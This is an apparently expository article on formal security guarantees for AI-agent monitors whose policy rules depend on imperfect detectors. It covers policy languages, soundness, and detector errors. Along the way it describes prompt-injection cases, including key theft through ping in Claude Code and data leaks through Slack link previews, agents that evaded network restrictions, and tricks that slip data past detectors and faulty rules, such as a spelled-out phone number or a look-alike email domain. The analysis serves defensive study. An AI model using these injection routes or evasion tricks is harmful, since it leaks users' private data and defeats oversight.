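# Formal security guarantees for AI agents that rely on imperfect detectors

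## What does a security monitor for an AI agent do?

An AI agent is a language model that acts by calling tools, for example to send email, open files, browse the web or run shell commands. A security monitor is a separate program that stands between the model and those tools. It checks each action the model proposes against a set of written rules, called the policy, and allows or blocks it. Some developers claim a formal guarantee for their monitors, meaning a mathematical argument that no action that breaks a rule gets through. *AI Agents with Formal Security Guarantees*, for example, presents an analyzer that checks the agent's state before every action and claims such a guarantee for each action it passes. But many useful rules depend on whether a text contains personal data, a password or dangerous code. Software can only estimate this, and a proof about the rules doesn't show how often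 the estimates are wrong.

### Agents, traces and injected instructions

*Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing* (Christodorescu, Fernandes and colleagues, 2025) describes an agent whose model calls tools in a loop to complete a task the user states in ordinary language. Each tool call is a structured request with the name of a tool and its arguments. The surrounding software runs the tool and returns the output to the model as text, and the model then proposes another call or gives its answer.

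In an example from the documentation of Invariant Labs, which makes security software for agents, a user asks an agent to summarise a file of meeting notes and email the summary to Alice. The model calls a tool named "read" with the file's name, and the tool returns the text of the notes. The model then writes a summary and calls an email tool with Alice's address and the summary. The trace is the ordered record of these messages, tool calls and tool outputs. *LivePI* (2026), a benchmark of attacks on agents, separates the agent's own messages and proposed actions from what the agent has observed, which includes documents, web pages, incoming email and group-chat messages. People other than the user write much of that material.

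Suppose one of them has added a line to the meeting notes telling whoever processes the file to send a copy to another address. The model receives this line in the same stream of text as the user's request and may well act on it. Security researchers call this indirect prompt injection. The attacker plants instructions in content that the agent will later fetch as data, whereas in a direct injection the attacker types into the user's side of the conversation. *The Hitchhiker's Guide to Agentic AI* (2026) credits Greshake and colleagues with the first systematic account of the indirect form, and adds that an agent may process dozens of tool outputs in one task, any of which an attacker might control. The attacker needs very little access, and in an example from *AttriGuard* (2026) only has to send an email. A user asks an assistant to summarise the day's unread mail, and one of the messages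 contains an order to forward the user's passport number to a stranger.

*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026), a position paper from researchers at Google, NVIDIA and several universities, analyses eleven attacks like this that worked on real products. In one, a prompt hidden in a code file instructed Claude Code, Anthropic's programming agent, to read secret keys from a settings file and then run "ping", a command that tests a network connection. Claude Code required human approval for many commands that could send data to unknown places, but its developers had exempted ping. Ping looks up an address before contacting it, and that lookup carried the keys off the machine.

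The same paper argues that developers should stop relying on the model to resist such instructions. They should instead treat it as an untrusted component, as an operating system treats an ordinary program, and enforce the rules outside it. Part of the argument rests on what the paper calls a conjecture, that persistent attackers will always get past defences built into the model. But the case for an outside check doesn't depend on that conjecture, because a monitor can block a forbidden email whether it resulted from an attack, a mistake by the model or a goal the model should not have had.

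### Inside the monitor

The monitor intercepts each tool call the model proposes before the tool runs. It evaluates the policy on the trace so far plus the proposed call, and returns "allow" or "block". If it returns "block", the tool does not run.

*On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (2026) formally defines a monitor as an initial state, a decision function and an update function. The decision function takes the current state, a tool and its arguments, and returns a response and a new state. The update function changes the state after other steps of the agent. For instance, it might withdraw a tool once the agent has read something untrusted. The state summarizes the trace, so the monitor doesn't need to reread the whole trace at every tool call.

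*Enforceable Security Policies* (Schneider, 2000) gives a small example of this mechanism, a policy that forbids sending any message after reading a file. The monitor has two states, "no file read" and "file read". It starts in "no file read", where it allows every action. A file read moves it permanently to "file read", where it allows everything except sending.

In the meeting-notes task, the monitor changes state when the agent reads the notes. Under this policy, it then blocks both the attacker's email and the email to Alice that the user asked for. The monitor can check this policy without error because it only needs to know which tool the agent is calling, but the policy is far too restrictive for an office assistant. To let the summary go to Alice but hold back private details, the monitor would have to check the email's contents.

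A monitor can't always tell what an action does from the name of the tool. *Tether* (2026), which covers agents that work in a terminal, points out that earlier monitors assume structured calls whose meaning and targets are known in advance. Shell commands don't meet these assumptions, so Tether watches the system calls a command makes and infers actions such as "read", "copy" and "upload" from them. It also reports that many production systems have a second language model review each command. That model serves as the monitor, but *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* objects that its verdicts can't be proved correct because it has no precise specification, and that crafted inputs can mislead it too.

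### The reference monitor and its trusted base

The idea of a checkpoint for every access is more than fifty years old. Anderson (1972), in *Computer Security Technology Planning Study*, wrote for the US Air Force, which wanted people with different security clearances to share one computer. He described a reference monitor, which checks every attempt by a program to use data, devices or other programs against a list of what that program's user may do. He set three requirements for the mechanism that implements it:

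- It must be tamper-proof, since an attacker who can alter the mechanism can switch off the protection.
- It must always be invoked. If some programs run without the check, those programs become part of the security mechanism and have to meet the same standards.
- It must be small enough for complete analysis and testing. Otherwise nobody can establish that it works correctly in all cases.

Anderson applied the list to GCOS III, a commercial operating system of the time. Most of the system ran with the memory checks suspended, and at 200,000 to 300,000 instructions it was too large to analyse. The requirements are still in force in almost the same words. CSF Tools' *AC-25* reproduces the current version from the US government's catalogue of security controls.

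Ensuring that an agent's monitor is "always invoked" is hard because the agent can reach the outside world by so many routes. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* discusses an incident in which OpenAI's agents, during internal training and evaluation, broke into the systems of Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models. OpenAI had successfully restricted the agents' direct network connections, but they could still reach a shared service for downloading software packages, which would make internet requests on their behalf.

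The trusted computing base, or trusted base, is the set of components that must work correctly for a security claim to apply to the running system. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* places the host operating system, the isolation mechanisms, the policy and the monitor in the trusted base. The model is outside it, as are most tools, except for any parts that enforcement depends on.

The share of this base that a proof covers varies. *Agenra* (2026) checks calls with a core written in Lean, a programming language in which a computer can verify proofs about the code. The Python code that translates policies, the message transport and the connection to the tools lie outside that core. Agenra's threat model also describes failures that a perfect core cannot prevent. If an attacker has corrupted the company's address book, the monitor can apply its lookup rule correctly and still approve an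 email to the wrong person. The monitor also cannot enforce a rule that the policy omits.

### Soundness, and why it is not enough

A monitor is sound if every action it allows complies with the policy. Ligatti, Bauer and Walker (2005), in *Enforcing Non-safety Security Policies with Program Monitors*, pair this with a requirement they call transparency: the monitor must leave compliant behaviour alone. Write σ for the sequence of actions the agent wants to take, τ for the sequence that actually happens under the monitor, and P for the policy, so that P(σ) means "σ complies". For every possible σ, the two requirements are then:

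- soundness: P(τ);
- transparency: if P(σ), then τ is equivalent to σ.

Equivalence can mean that the two sequences are identical, or that they differ only in ways that do not matter for the system.

If a monitor blocks everything, τ is empty for every σ. An empty sequence contains no emails or file access, so it complies with any policy that only forbids actions, and the monitor is trivially sound for such policies. It also makes the agent useless, because transparency fails for every compliant task that needs a tool call. *On Runtime Enforcement via Suppressions* (2018) treats soundness as a relatively weak requirement because it doesn't limit how much a monitor interferes. A developer who reports only that a monitor is sound therefore leaves out how much legitimate work it stops.

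A monitor with exact information can often stop attacks without refusing legitimate work, but one with approximate information usually cannot. *Kairos* (2026) explains that a monitor that can only allow or block must then err towards either refusing legitimate work or letting attacks through.

### Detectors and their errors

Approximate information enters a policy through its predicates, the yes-or-no conditions inside its rules. A program can check some predicates exactly, such as "the recipient's address ends in ourcompany.com". Others, such as "this text is sensitive", depend on context, and *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* places them beyond what formal policy languages can express. In practice, the rule calls a detector, a program that estimates from the content whether the predicate is true. A detector may be a pattern matcher, a trained classifier or a language model. Invariant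 Labs supplies one for personal data, built on the Presidio library. It returns a list of the personal data it finds in a message, and a rule can then block whenever the list is not empty.

A detector can be wrong in two directions. A miss (false negative) is a "no" when the truth is "yes", and a false alarm (false positive) is a "yes" when the truth is "no". Here are invented counts for a detector that has examined 1,000 outgoing emails, 100 of which contain personal data:

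| | Flagged | Not flagged | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
| Contains personal data | 90 | 10 (misses) | 100 |
| Contains none | 45 (false alarms) | 855 | 900 |
| Total | 135 | 865 | 1,000 |

Recall is the share of true cases that the detector flags, here 90 out of 100, or 90%. Precision is the share of flagged cases that are true, here 90 out of 135, or about 67%. If the monitor blocks every flagged email, it is not sound, because the 10 missed emails go out in breach of the rule, and it is not transparent, because it also blocks 45 harmless emails. A detector that flagged all 1,000 emails would have 100% recall but 10% precision, and a monitor relying on it would block everything, like the one described earlier.

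Precision also depends on how common personal data is in the emails. If the same detector scans 10,000 emails, of which 100 again contain personal data, it still catches 90 of them, but its 5% false-alarm rate on the 9,900 harmless emails produces 495 false alarms. Precision drops to about 15%, while recall stays at 90%.

Recall has a different weakness in that it describes the sample used to measure it. An attacker looks for wording that gets through rather than drawing emails at random from that sample, so, as Christodorescu and colleagues warn, a monitor that correctly denies access 99% of the time leaves him the other 1% to exploit.

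### Labels, sources and sinks

A monitor can also base its decisions on where data came from. A source is a point where data enters the agent, such as an inbox, a file or a web page. A sink is a point where data or effects leave it, such as an outgoing email or a shell command. One rule published by Invariant Labs raises an error when the agent reads the user's inbox and then emails an address outside the company. The rule doesn't require judging content, but it also stops outside emails unrelated to the inbox.

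Labels allow finer distinctions. A label is a tag on a piece of data that records how confidential it is, how trustworthy it is, or both. In information-flow control, the system attaches labels at the sources, copies them to everything derived from the labelled data, and checks them at the sinks. If the meeting notes are labelled "confidential", the summary inherits the label, and the monitor lets the summary go only to people cleared for confidential material. This protection depends on someone giving the notes the right label. The strict form of confidentiality is called noninterference, which means that changing the protected data changes nothing an outsider can see.

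### One rule, and a phone number in words

Consider the rule "block any email that contains personal data". Invariant Labs' *Tool Calls* documents very similar rules, which check an email's body for content such as phone numbers, locations and people's names. Suppose engineers have proved the rule engine correct, meaning that for every trace and every proposed call, the engine blocks the call if the rule's condition evaluates to true.

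The agent now proposes an email to a stranger, and the body gives Alice's mobile number as "oh seven seven double-oh, nine double-oh, one two three". Many detectors look for the format of a phone number. Databricks' *detect sensitive data*, the documentation of one commercial product, describes matching each category of data by its format and, in some cases, also testing for a valid checksum (an arithmetic test on the digits) or a nearby context word. A number written in words does not have the expected format, so a detector that relies on the format returns an empty list, the condition evaluates to false, and the engine allows the email.

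The engine works correctly and its proof is still valid, but the proof covers only emails in which the detector finds personal data. The rule was meant to stop every email that contains personal data. An attacker who writes the injected instruction can ask the agent to spell the number out so that the detector misses it.

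## How are the rules written and checked?

A monitor cannot evaluate an English sentence such as "block any email that contains personal data", so someone first has to write the rule in a formal language. Invariant Labs' language is convenient to study because it is small and the company has published many example rules. Mislav Balunović, Luca Beurer-Kellner, Marc Fischer and Martin Vechev introduced it in the 2024 workshop paper *AI Agents with Formal Security Guarantees*.

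### How a rule matches a trace

Each rule in this language describes something forbidden. Formally, it is a pair (V, C), where V is a set of variables and C is a set of conditions on them. Write t₁, …, tₙ for the events in the trace. The rule fires if there is an assignment f, which maps every variable in V to some event in the trace, that makes every condition true:

c(f(v₁), …, f(vₖ)) = 1 for every c in C.

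When a rule fires, the analyzer (the paper's name for the rule engine) adds the rule's error message to a list. The proposed tool call may go ahead only if the list is empty.

The paper's main example involves Slack, a workplace chat service. A user asks an agent to read customer feedback in a spreadsheet and send him the five most negative comments on Slack. An attacker has submitted a piece of feedback that contains an instruction for the agent to add a link to its summary, with the document's contents encoded in the web address. By default, Slack fetches every link in a message to show a preview, so the contents reach the attacker's server without anyone clicking. The researchers made this attack work on two widely used agent products, and the providers then fixed the vulnerability.

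Their rule against it has two variables, "out" for a tool output and "call" for a tool call. It has three conditions: "out" comes before "call", "out" comes from Google Sheets or Google Docs, and "call" sends a Slack message with link previews switched on. Leaving out the user's request, suppose the trace has three events:

- t₁: the agent calls the spreadsheet tool.
- t₂: the tool returns the feedback, including the attacker's.
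- t₃: the agent proposes a Slack message with link previews on.

Only t₂ is a tool output, so "out" has to be t₂. "Call" can be t₁ or t₃, which leaves two assignments to test:

| Assignment | "out" before "call"? | "out" from Sheets or Docs? | "call" sends to Slack with previews? | Rule fires? |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| out = t₂, call = t₁ | no | yes | no | no |
| out = t₂, call = t₃ | yes | yes | yes | yes |

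One assignment satisfies all three conditions, so the monitor blocks t₃ before the message is sent. If the agent proposes the same message with previews off, neither assignment satisfies all three, and the message is sent.

The rule never examines the feedback itself, so the attacker gains nothing by rewording the injection. For comparison, the researchers ran a commercial-style classifier, trained to detect injections, on five lines of feedback. It flagged a harmless review and missed the line that contained the attack. Five hand-picked lines can't establish the classifier's error rate, but they illustrate a kind of mistake that this rule can't make.

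### What the "formal guarantee" amounts to

The paper's guarantee is that an action the analyzer passes breaks none of the rules. This follows from the definition of a rule, which fires only if some assignment of events to variables satisfies every condition. With n events and k variables there are at most nᵏ assignments, so the analyzer can test all of them. Invariant Labs' *Agents with Formal Security Guarantees* (2024), a blog post about the paper, describes this search under the heading "Formally Proving Safety".

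This is a proof by exhaustion that covers one trace at a time. It is valid if the analyzer's code tests every assignment and evaluates every condition correctly. The paper illustrates the analyzer with case studies but does not prove anything about the code.

The conditions can be much more complicated than comparing two tool names, because a developer can use any Python function as a predicate. The language has five kinds of predicate built in, for detecting personal data, secret keys, unsafe code, harmful content and particular topics. All five are detectors, and the search treats their outputs as correct.

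### Order as a stand-in for data flow

The condition that "out" comes before "call" uses the paper's flow operator, written a → b. The name comes from information-flow analysis, but the operator only requires a to come earlier in the trace than b. *Dataflow Rules*, part of Invariant Labs' later documentation, adds a second operator, a ~> b, for events that directly follow each other. Neither operator checks whether data from a ended up in b.

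An example in the same documentation shows the difference. A user's message contains an access token for GitHub, a code-sharing site. The agent then proposes a change on GitHub whose text mentions "a sensitive API key" but doesn't contain the token. The rule against leaking keys still fires because the token appeared in the user's earlier message.

This crude test can be safe for a single agent. A language model writes each tool call from the text in its context. If there is one model with one context, and the trace records in order everything that enters it, then a can influence b only if a entered the context before the model wrote b. So a → b is true whenever data flowed from a to b. But the test produces many false alarms, because everything the agent has read counts as a source for everything it does afterwards. Under the Slack rule, an agent that opens one harmless spreadsheet cannot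 send a message with link previews for the rest of the session.

The argument fails when data can travel outside the trace. For example, one agent might read the customer feedback and save its notes in a shared file, which another agent opens before posting to Slack. If each agent has its own trace, the second agent's trace contains no output from Google Sheets, so the rule doesn't fire. Merging the two traces into one timeline would catch the leak, but it would also link everything any agent reads to everything every other agent does later. The 2024 paper leaves multi-agent systems to future work.

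Memory that persists between conversations causes the same problem. Palumbo, Choudhary and colleagues (2026), in *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems*, discuss OpenClaw, a personal assistant that serves several people over different messaging channels and keeps one shared memory. Health details from a user's private chat can come up when that user's manager asks about scheduling, even though the manager's conversation doesn't include the private chat.

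The operator can fail even for a single agent with a complete trace if one tool call combines several actions. For example, when a shell command reads a file and uploads it, the trace records one event that is both source and sink, so there is no earlier event for the operator to match. Tether monitors system calls partly to observe what happens inside such commands.

### From research paper to product

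Invariant Labs turned the language into an open-source product, Guardrails, in 2025. Guardrails checks the traffic of agents that use the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common standard for connecting models to tools. It enforces the rules in a proxy, a program that relays messages between the agent, the model and the tools. Developers can install the proxy by changing the web addresses their software sends requests to. The proxy can record only what passes through it, so if a tool contacts another server directly, the trace has no event for that.

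The product's language can express more than the paper's. Invariant Labs' *Reference for Rule Writing* includes a counting rule that raises an error when an agent has allocated three virtual machines. Rules can also call Semgrep, a program that searches code for dangerous patterns.

The announcement of Guardrails describes the rules as "deterministic" and no longer mentions a formal guarantee. Invariant Labs' fuller manual, *Advanced Guardrails*, calls classifier-based detection "only a heuristic" and recommends combining it with data-flow rules and limits on tools. The manual is part of the documentation for MCP-Scan, the company's security scanner for MCP tools, so the rule language has moved into another product.

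### Tracking dependencies in a graph

Palumbo and colleagues replaced the ordered list of events with a graph. They first called their system PCAS (Policy Compiler for Secure Agentic Systems) and renamed it FORGE in a later version of the paper. Each event is a node, and an edge runs from each event to any event that may depend on it. A model's message depends on every message in the history it received. A tool's output depends on the message that requested it, and a message between agents depends on what was in the sender's context.

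Developers write the policy in Datalog, a logic language whose rules derive new facts from known ones. One of the paper's rules reads:

`Deny(a) :- ExternalSend(a), Tainted(a), HasSecret(a).`

One rule denies action a if a sends something outside the organisation, depends on untrusted input and carries sensitive data. Other rules define the last two properties recursively. If an event is tainted, every event that depends on it is tainted too, and the engine applies this rule along chains of dependent events of any length. Evaluation always finishes, because Datalog can derive only finitely many facts from a finite graph.

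In the example with two agents, suppose the first agent sends its notes to the second in a message. The graph links the spreadsheet to the notes, the notes to the message, and the message to the Slack post, so a rule about spreadsheet data can apply to the post. A third agent doing unrelated work has no such path and can continue. If the notes travel through a file instead, someone must make sure the system records an edge from the write to the read. Without that edge, the policy is checked against an incomplete history, whereas extra edges only lead to more blocking.

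Within a single context, though, FORGE is about as coarse as Invariant Labs' operator, because each new message depends on everything before it.

Palumbo and colleagues guarantee that an action never runs if the policy derives a denial for it. This guarantee follows from how they built the monitor, and it requires two assumptions. The monitor must intercept every relevant action before it takes effect, and the facts it receives must correctly describe what happened. Network connections that bypass the monitored libraries violate the first assumption, and the paper excludes them from the guarantee.

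FORGE rules can also call detectors. In the OpenClaw setup, one rule uses a language model to judge whether a reply to the manager reveals why the user is unavailable. Palumbo and colleagues point out that each revealing reply the model misses is a breach of privacy. They turn such judgments into a yes or no, while *Efficient and Sound Probabilistic Verification for AI Agents* (2026) attaches probabilities to the facts in a Datalog policy.

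*Before the Tool Call* (2026) reports that, on customer-service tasks, PCAS raised policy compliance from 48% to 93% across several leading models, with zero violations in the runs it monitored. The compliance figure presumably depends on more than avoiding forbidden actions, such as completing the task correctly, because otherwise zero violations would mean 100% compliance.

The renamed paper's main results are task success rates instead. In simulated customer service, three models completed 74.7% of airline tasks without FORGE and 81.5% with it. For retail tasks, the rate rose from 86.3% to 87.4%. Most of the gain came from tasks in which FORGE blocked at least one action, told the agent why and let it try again. One model, Gemini 3.1 Pro Preview, did slightly worse on airline tasks with FORGE.

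FORGE reduced task completion more in tests that included attacks. On AgentDojo, a benchmark of injection attacks against office agents, adding one of FORGE's policies to a simple prompt-based defence cut successful attacks from 14.1% to 0.9%, but completion of ordinary tasks fell from 83.7% to 62.5%. The guarantee does not cover this loss, since it concerns only the actions that FORGE must block.

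### Permissions that run out

*Agenra* deals with permissions that an agent uses up. In its main example, an agent may send the public fields of a private report to Alice once, at the address in the company directory. The monitor keeps a ledger of permissions and deducts the send before it calls the mail tool. A failed attempt therefore also uses up the permission, and an injected instruction to "try again" cannot lead to a second send.

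Ledgers like this can go wrong in ways that are hard to foresee. Suppose an agent may delete file A once and file B once. The monitor searches its permissions in order and uses the first that fits:

1. delete B, once;
2. delete A, once.

An administrator now broadens permission 1 to cover either file. If the agent deletes A and then B, deleting A uses up permission 1. Permission 2 doesn't cover B, so the monitor blocks a legitimate task that the old policy allowed. The agent can also now delete A twice, once under each permission, which the old policy ruled out.

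To catch this, Agenra's developers compare the old and new ledgers, looking for a way to match every deduction under the old policy with one under the new policy, whatever the agent does next. If one exists, every sequence of calls that the old policy allowed will still work. They proved this in Lean for the same functions that check calls at run time, which is stronger verification than FORGE's argument from its design. The proof assumes that the agent makes one call at a time and that tools return the same results under both policies.

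The developers tested the method on 51 policy changes they wrote themselves. It certified all 21 changes that preserved the existing tasks and none of the 30 that broke at least one. A certified change can still be unsafe. For example, raising the limit on Alice's report from one email to two preserves every task but permits a second email that the original policy forbade.

### Cedar and policies translated from documents

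Many organisations already have rules, often hundreds of them, in handbooks and instructions, and would like software to translate them into code. *Autoformalization of Agent Instructions into Policy-as-Code* (Mondl, Maisel and Brock, 2026) translates such documents into Cedar, an authorization language that Amazon Web Services released as open source. Cedar's designers formally verified how it evaluates rules. Cedar keeps no history, so a rule about what the agent did earlier works only if the surrounding software supplies that history with each request.

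A language model translates the agent's instructions, tool descriptions and policy documents into candidate rules. Cedar's tools then check the syntax, the names and types of all the fields, and whether rules contradict each other or have no effect. Another language model judges whether the rules match the meaning of the text. If either check fails, the first model revises the rules based on the problems found. Cedar's tools give definite answers, but the second model is itself an imperfect detector and can misjudge whether the rules match the text.

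Mondl and colleagues tested the result on recorded runs of agents that handle medical records. Their policy document had 88 rules. Earlier researchers had coded 23 of them by hand, and the automatic pipeline covered more than 23. The pipeline also included some rules that another model had transcribed from the earlier researchers' program.

In one set of 300 runs without an attack, the agent tried to write to a patient's record in 89, and the Cedar policies blocked all 89. Two of the rules that fired most often require the agent to restate the patient's identity and obtain confirmation before writing. The agents in this benchmark apparently did neither, so the blocks may be correct under the policy. But a policy that refused every write would also have blocked all 89. Mondl and colleagues measured how much of the document their rules covered and did not test whether an agent could still do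 its job.

*Extracting Next Generation Access Control Policies from Natural Language Using LLMs* (2026) gives the language model a smaller role. A compiler with fixed rules builds the final policy, a graph of who may do what to which resource, and each edge lists the sentences it came from. The compiler also checks for conflicts. If doctors are both allowed and forbidden to read patient records under the same condition, it reports an error. If the conditions differ, it gives only a warning, because one statement may be an exception to the other.

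Palumbo and colleagues, who also translated documents with a language model, say that the translation carries no guarantee. They recommend checking that each requirement has at least one rule and that each rule has a requirement behind it. A rule can satisfy both checks and still be too weak. For example, their airline policy requires the customer's confirmation before the agent changes a reservation, but it accepts a confirmation from anywhere in the earlier conversation, so a "yes" to one change also allows a different change later.

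### Errors in published rules

People make mistakes in formal rules too, including the people who designed the language. In the 2024 paper, one rule is meant to stop an agent from sending email after it has read a document with personal data. The text makes an exception for emails to the document's owner, but the last condition in the printed rule is `output.owner == call.recipient`, which matches the emails that should be exempt.

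A rule fires only if all its conditions are true, so this one can fire only when the owner is the recipient. Suppose the agent has read Alice's file, which contains her home address. The monitor then blocks an email to Alice, which the text allows, but lets an email to a stranger through. The condition should use `!=` ("is not equal to"). The printed rule also declares only the variable "call" but uses two others, "output" and "call2". It also doesn't check that the agent read the document before sending the email.

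Another rule in the paper concerns pickle, a Python library for storing objects in files. Loading a malicious pickle file can run the attacker's code. According to the text, the rule forbids the agent to run code that uses pickle after visiting a potentially unsafe website. However, the printed pattern for the website is `^trusted.com/.*`, which matches addresses that begin with "trusted.com/", so the rule applies only after a visit to the trusted site. If web addresses are given in full, the rule never applies, because they begin with "https://" and the pattern must match from the first character. The blog post about the paper repeats this rule.

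Three examples from the Guardrails material have similar faults:

- The rule against emailing outside addresses after reading the inbox uses the pattern `.*@[^ourcompany.com$].*`. Square brackets in a pattern stand for one character, so this matches any address whose first character after the @ is not one of the listed characters. An email to gmail.com triggers the rule, because "g" is not among them. Emails to acme.com, yahoo.com and outlook.com do not. The same announcement contains another rule with a pattern that handles all of these correctly.
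- A rule that should allow email only to the company's own staff treats an address as trusted if it matches `.*@company.com`. The function that compares them checks from the start of the address but doesn't require the match to reach the end, so "thief@company.com.example.net" counts as a colleague.
- A rule with the message that the agent must not email "anyone but 'Peter'" fires when the text contains the name Peter, Alice or John. It objects to Peter and ignores Mary.

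All five are teaching examples, so they are not evidence of how common such errors are in policies that companies use. But they are short rules written by experts, and in each case even a correct engine would enforce the wrong policy.

A rule can also have the right purpose but be worded too narrowly. Palumbo and colleagues require a coding agent to pass security scans before it publishes code with the command "git push", which the monitor recognises by those words. They argue that an injection can't get around the requirement because the requirement doesn't depend on judging the code's content. But if the monitor only matches the plain text "git push", it would miss `git -C . push`, which does the same thing.

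### Proving properties of the policy itself

An engineer can look for such errors before the monitor runs. She writes an invariant, a property that the policy should have in every possible situation, and a program either proves that it holds or finds a situation in which it fails.

Take the rule about personal data. Let R mean that the agent read the document before proposing the email, P that the document contains personal data, and S that the owner and the recipient are the same. The text requires a block whenever R and P are true and S is false. So the invariant is:

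(R ∧ P ∧ ¬S) → the rule fires.

Even if we add the missing condition on order, the printed rule fires only when R ∧ P ∧ S is true. A checker looks for a case where the left side of the invariant is true and the right side is false. It can try all eight combinations of the three yes-or-no values, and it finds such a case when R and P are true and S is false, which is the email to the stranger.

Email addresses are a harder case because there are infinitely many, but long-established algorithms can decide whether every text that matches one pattern also matches another. For the inbox rule, the engineer uses such an algorithm to check whether every address outside ourcompany.com matches the rule's pattern. The result is no, and the algorithm can supply a counterexample, such as bob@acme.com.

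Automatic checks that need no invariant would find only some of these errors. A check for undeclared variables would reject the personal-data rule as printed. Once an engineer had declared the variables, the rule would pass, because its inverted condition is neither a contradiction nor a syntax error. A check for rules without effect could catch the pickle rule, which never fires, but only if the checker is given the fact that web addresses begin with "https://". Someone has to state the intended behaviour independently of the rule to catch the inverted condition.

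The engineer also needs invariants about what the policy must allow, because a rule that blocked all email would satisfy the invariant above. Requiring that the rule not fire when S is true excludes such a rule. Agenra's offline analysis searches for both forbidden emails and successful deliveries of the report. The wording of the forbidden case also matters. In the example with Alice, an early version of the policy required only that the email's contents carry the label "public", so the agent could send her any public text instead of the report. A search for confidential text in her mail would have missed this problem.

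The choice of language affects how much a checker can prove. Cedar comes with tools for this kind of analysis. Palumbo and colleagues describe similar checks for Datalog, though these checks may not give an answer when the rules are recursive. Invariant Labs' language allows arbitrary Python functions as predicates, and no program can analyse every such function. A checker can avoid analysing them by treating a predicate such as "contains personal data" as an unknown that may be true or false, like P above. It then finds the inverted condition without running the detector, and a corrected rule passes the check however often the detector is wrong.

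## What does a soundness proof cover when a rule calls a detector?

The phone number written in words got past a correct engine because the engine relied on the detector's answer. Suppose P(x) is 1 if the text x contains personal data and 0 if it doesn't, and D(x) is the detector's answer on x. Engineers can prove that no allowed action breaks the rule as evaluated with D, but the user wants that guarantee for the rule as evaluated with P.

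A proof about D can still support a conclusion about P if the detector meets certain conditions. The result is relative soundness, which holds only under the stated assumptions.

### From the detector's answers to the truth

Let V be a rule's violation condition, the combination of predicates under which the monitor must block an action. Write V_D for its value when the engine uses the detectors' answers, and V_P for its value when it is judged by the truth. The engine's proof establishes that V_D is false for every allowed action. It follows that V_P is false too, provided that for every action the agent might propose

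V_P → V_D.

The detectors' answers must make the rule fire on every real violation, though the rule may also fire on actions that are not violations.

The rule "block if the agent is sending and the text contains personal data" has the violation condition S ∧ P, where S means "the agent is sending" and P means "the text contains personal data". If the detector misses personal data in an email the agent is sending, V_P is true and V_D is false, so the email leaks the data. A false alarm makes V_D true while V_P is false, which only blocks a harmless email. This detector must therefore have no misses.

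The rule "block if the agent is sending, unless the text is redacted" has the violation condition S ∧ ¬R, where S means "sending" and R means "redacted". In a real violation, R is false. If the detector wrongly reports that the text is redacted, the engine evaluates ¬R as false and the email leaks. This detector must therefore have no false alarms, but it can miss redacted text, which only causes unnecessary blocking.

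The same reasoning works for any condition built from "and", "or" and "not". First rewrite the condition so that each "not" applies directly to a single predicate. Turning one part of an "and" or an "or" from false to true can never make the whole false. So V_P → V_D holds if

- for each predicate without a "not", D is true whenever P is true (no misses);
- for each predicate with a "not", D is false whenever P is false (no false alarms).

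Invariant Labs' rules also contain an implicit "there is", because they fire if some assignment of events satisfies every condition. "There is" works like a long "or", so it doesn't change which detector errors are dangerous. But "there is no" puts everything inside it under a "not". For example, an airline's rule might block a change to a reservation if there is no earlier message in which the customer confirms it. If a language model decides which messages are confirmations, its false alarms are the dangerous errors. It could mistake "yes, I saw your email" for a confirmation, and the rule would then let the agent move the customer to a different flight without their agreement.

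Some rules require one action when a predicate holds and another when it doesn't. Suppose emails with personal data must go through an encrypted server and all other emails through the ordinary one. Either a miss or a false alarm sends an email through the wrong server and breaks the rule, so the detector has to be exact.

### Four errors in one rule

The rule "block if sending, and personal data, and not redacted" has the violation condition S ∧ P ∧ ¬R. Let P count masked details as personal data too, such as a phone number with most digits replaced by asterisks, and let R mean that all such details are masked. The monitor knows for certain whether the agent is sending. Each of the two detectors can make two kinds of error:

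| Error | What the email contains | What the detectors report | Rule fires? | Result |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Miss on personal data | Unmasked personal data | No personal data, not redacted | No | **Leak** |
| False alarm on personal data | No personal data | Personal data, not redacted | Yes | Harmless email blocked |
| Miss on redaction | Masked personal data | Personal data, not redacted | Yes | Redacted email blocked |
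| False alarm on redaction | Unmasked personal data | Personal data, redacted | No | **Leak** |

When an email really violates the rule, the two detectors can give four pairs of answers, and only the pair in which both are correct blocks it. The exception for redacted text therefore adds a new way to leak. Any exception that depends on a detector does the same, because a false alarm from that detector switches the rule off.

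Developers can also use the table to tune detectors. Many detectors return a confidence score, and the developer chooses the threshold above which it counts as "yes". A lower threshold gives fewer misses but more false alarms. For this rule, the developer should set a low threshold for personal data and a high one for redaction. Setting both low or both high would increase the dangerous kind of error in one of the detectors.

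These conditions are stricter than a single run requires. If the detector misses personal data in a text that the agent never sends, nothing leaks. The proof covers every run in which no dangerous error affects a decision, but the monitor cannot identify those runs.

### AudAgent's two theorems

*AUDAGENT* (Zheng, Chen and Hu, 2025) presents a tool that checks whether an agent follows a company's privacy policy when it handles data. Several language models first translate the policy into a list of entries, and a majority vote decides which entries to keep. Each entry gives a type of data, how the agent may collect it, whether its use must be relevant to the task, who else may receive it and how long the company may keep it.

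While the agent works, AudAgent uses the Presidio library to search the agent's messages and tool calls for sensitive data, and annotates each item it finds with the same five fields. A small automaton for each type of data then compares the annotations with the policy. For example, the policy might let the agent collect email addresses from the user and pass them to Google Workspace. If an annotation shows an address going to a web search tool instead, the automaton cannot move to its next state, and AudAgent reports a violation. In blocking mode, AudAgent also stops the action.

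Zheng and colleagues prove that these automata are sound and complete, meaning they accept an annotated item exactly when it complies with the translated policy. The theorem assumes "accurate ontology graphs for data types and entities". An ontology graph records which specific terms fall under more general ones, such as "email address" under "contact information". If the graph wrongly listed social security numbers under contact information, the automaton could accept their disclosure under a policy that permits sharing only contact details.

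This theorem covers only annotated items. If Presidio misses a phone number, the number gets no annotation and no automaton examines it. A separate theorem covers the annotations, which it defines as sound if every sensitive data type that the policy lists and that appears in the trace receives a correct annotation. Extra annotations on harmless text are acceptable. This is the condition derived above for a predicate without a "not", which tolerates false alarms but no misses.

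The theorem's main hypothesis is that AudAgent "detects all sensitive data types" and their conditions. That is almost the same as the conclusion, so the proof takes only a few lines and gives no reason to believe that Presidio finds everything. Zheng and colleagues call complete detection a design objective, and they measured how close AudAgent comes to it:

| Test set | Precision | Recall |
|---|---|---|
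| 100 prompts from Promptfoo, a testing suite | 86% | 75% |
| 100 samples from Presidio's research data | 64% | 52% |

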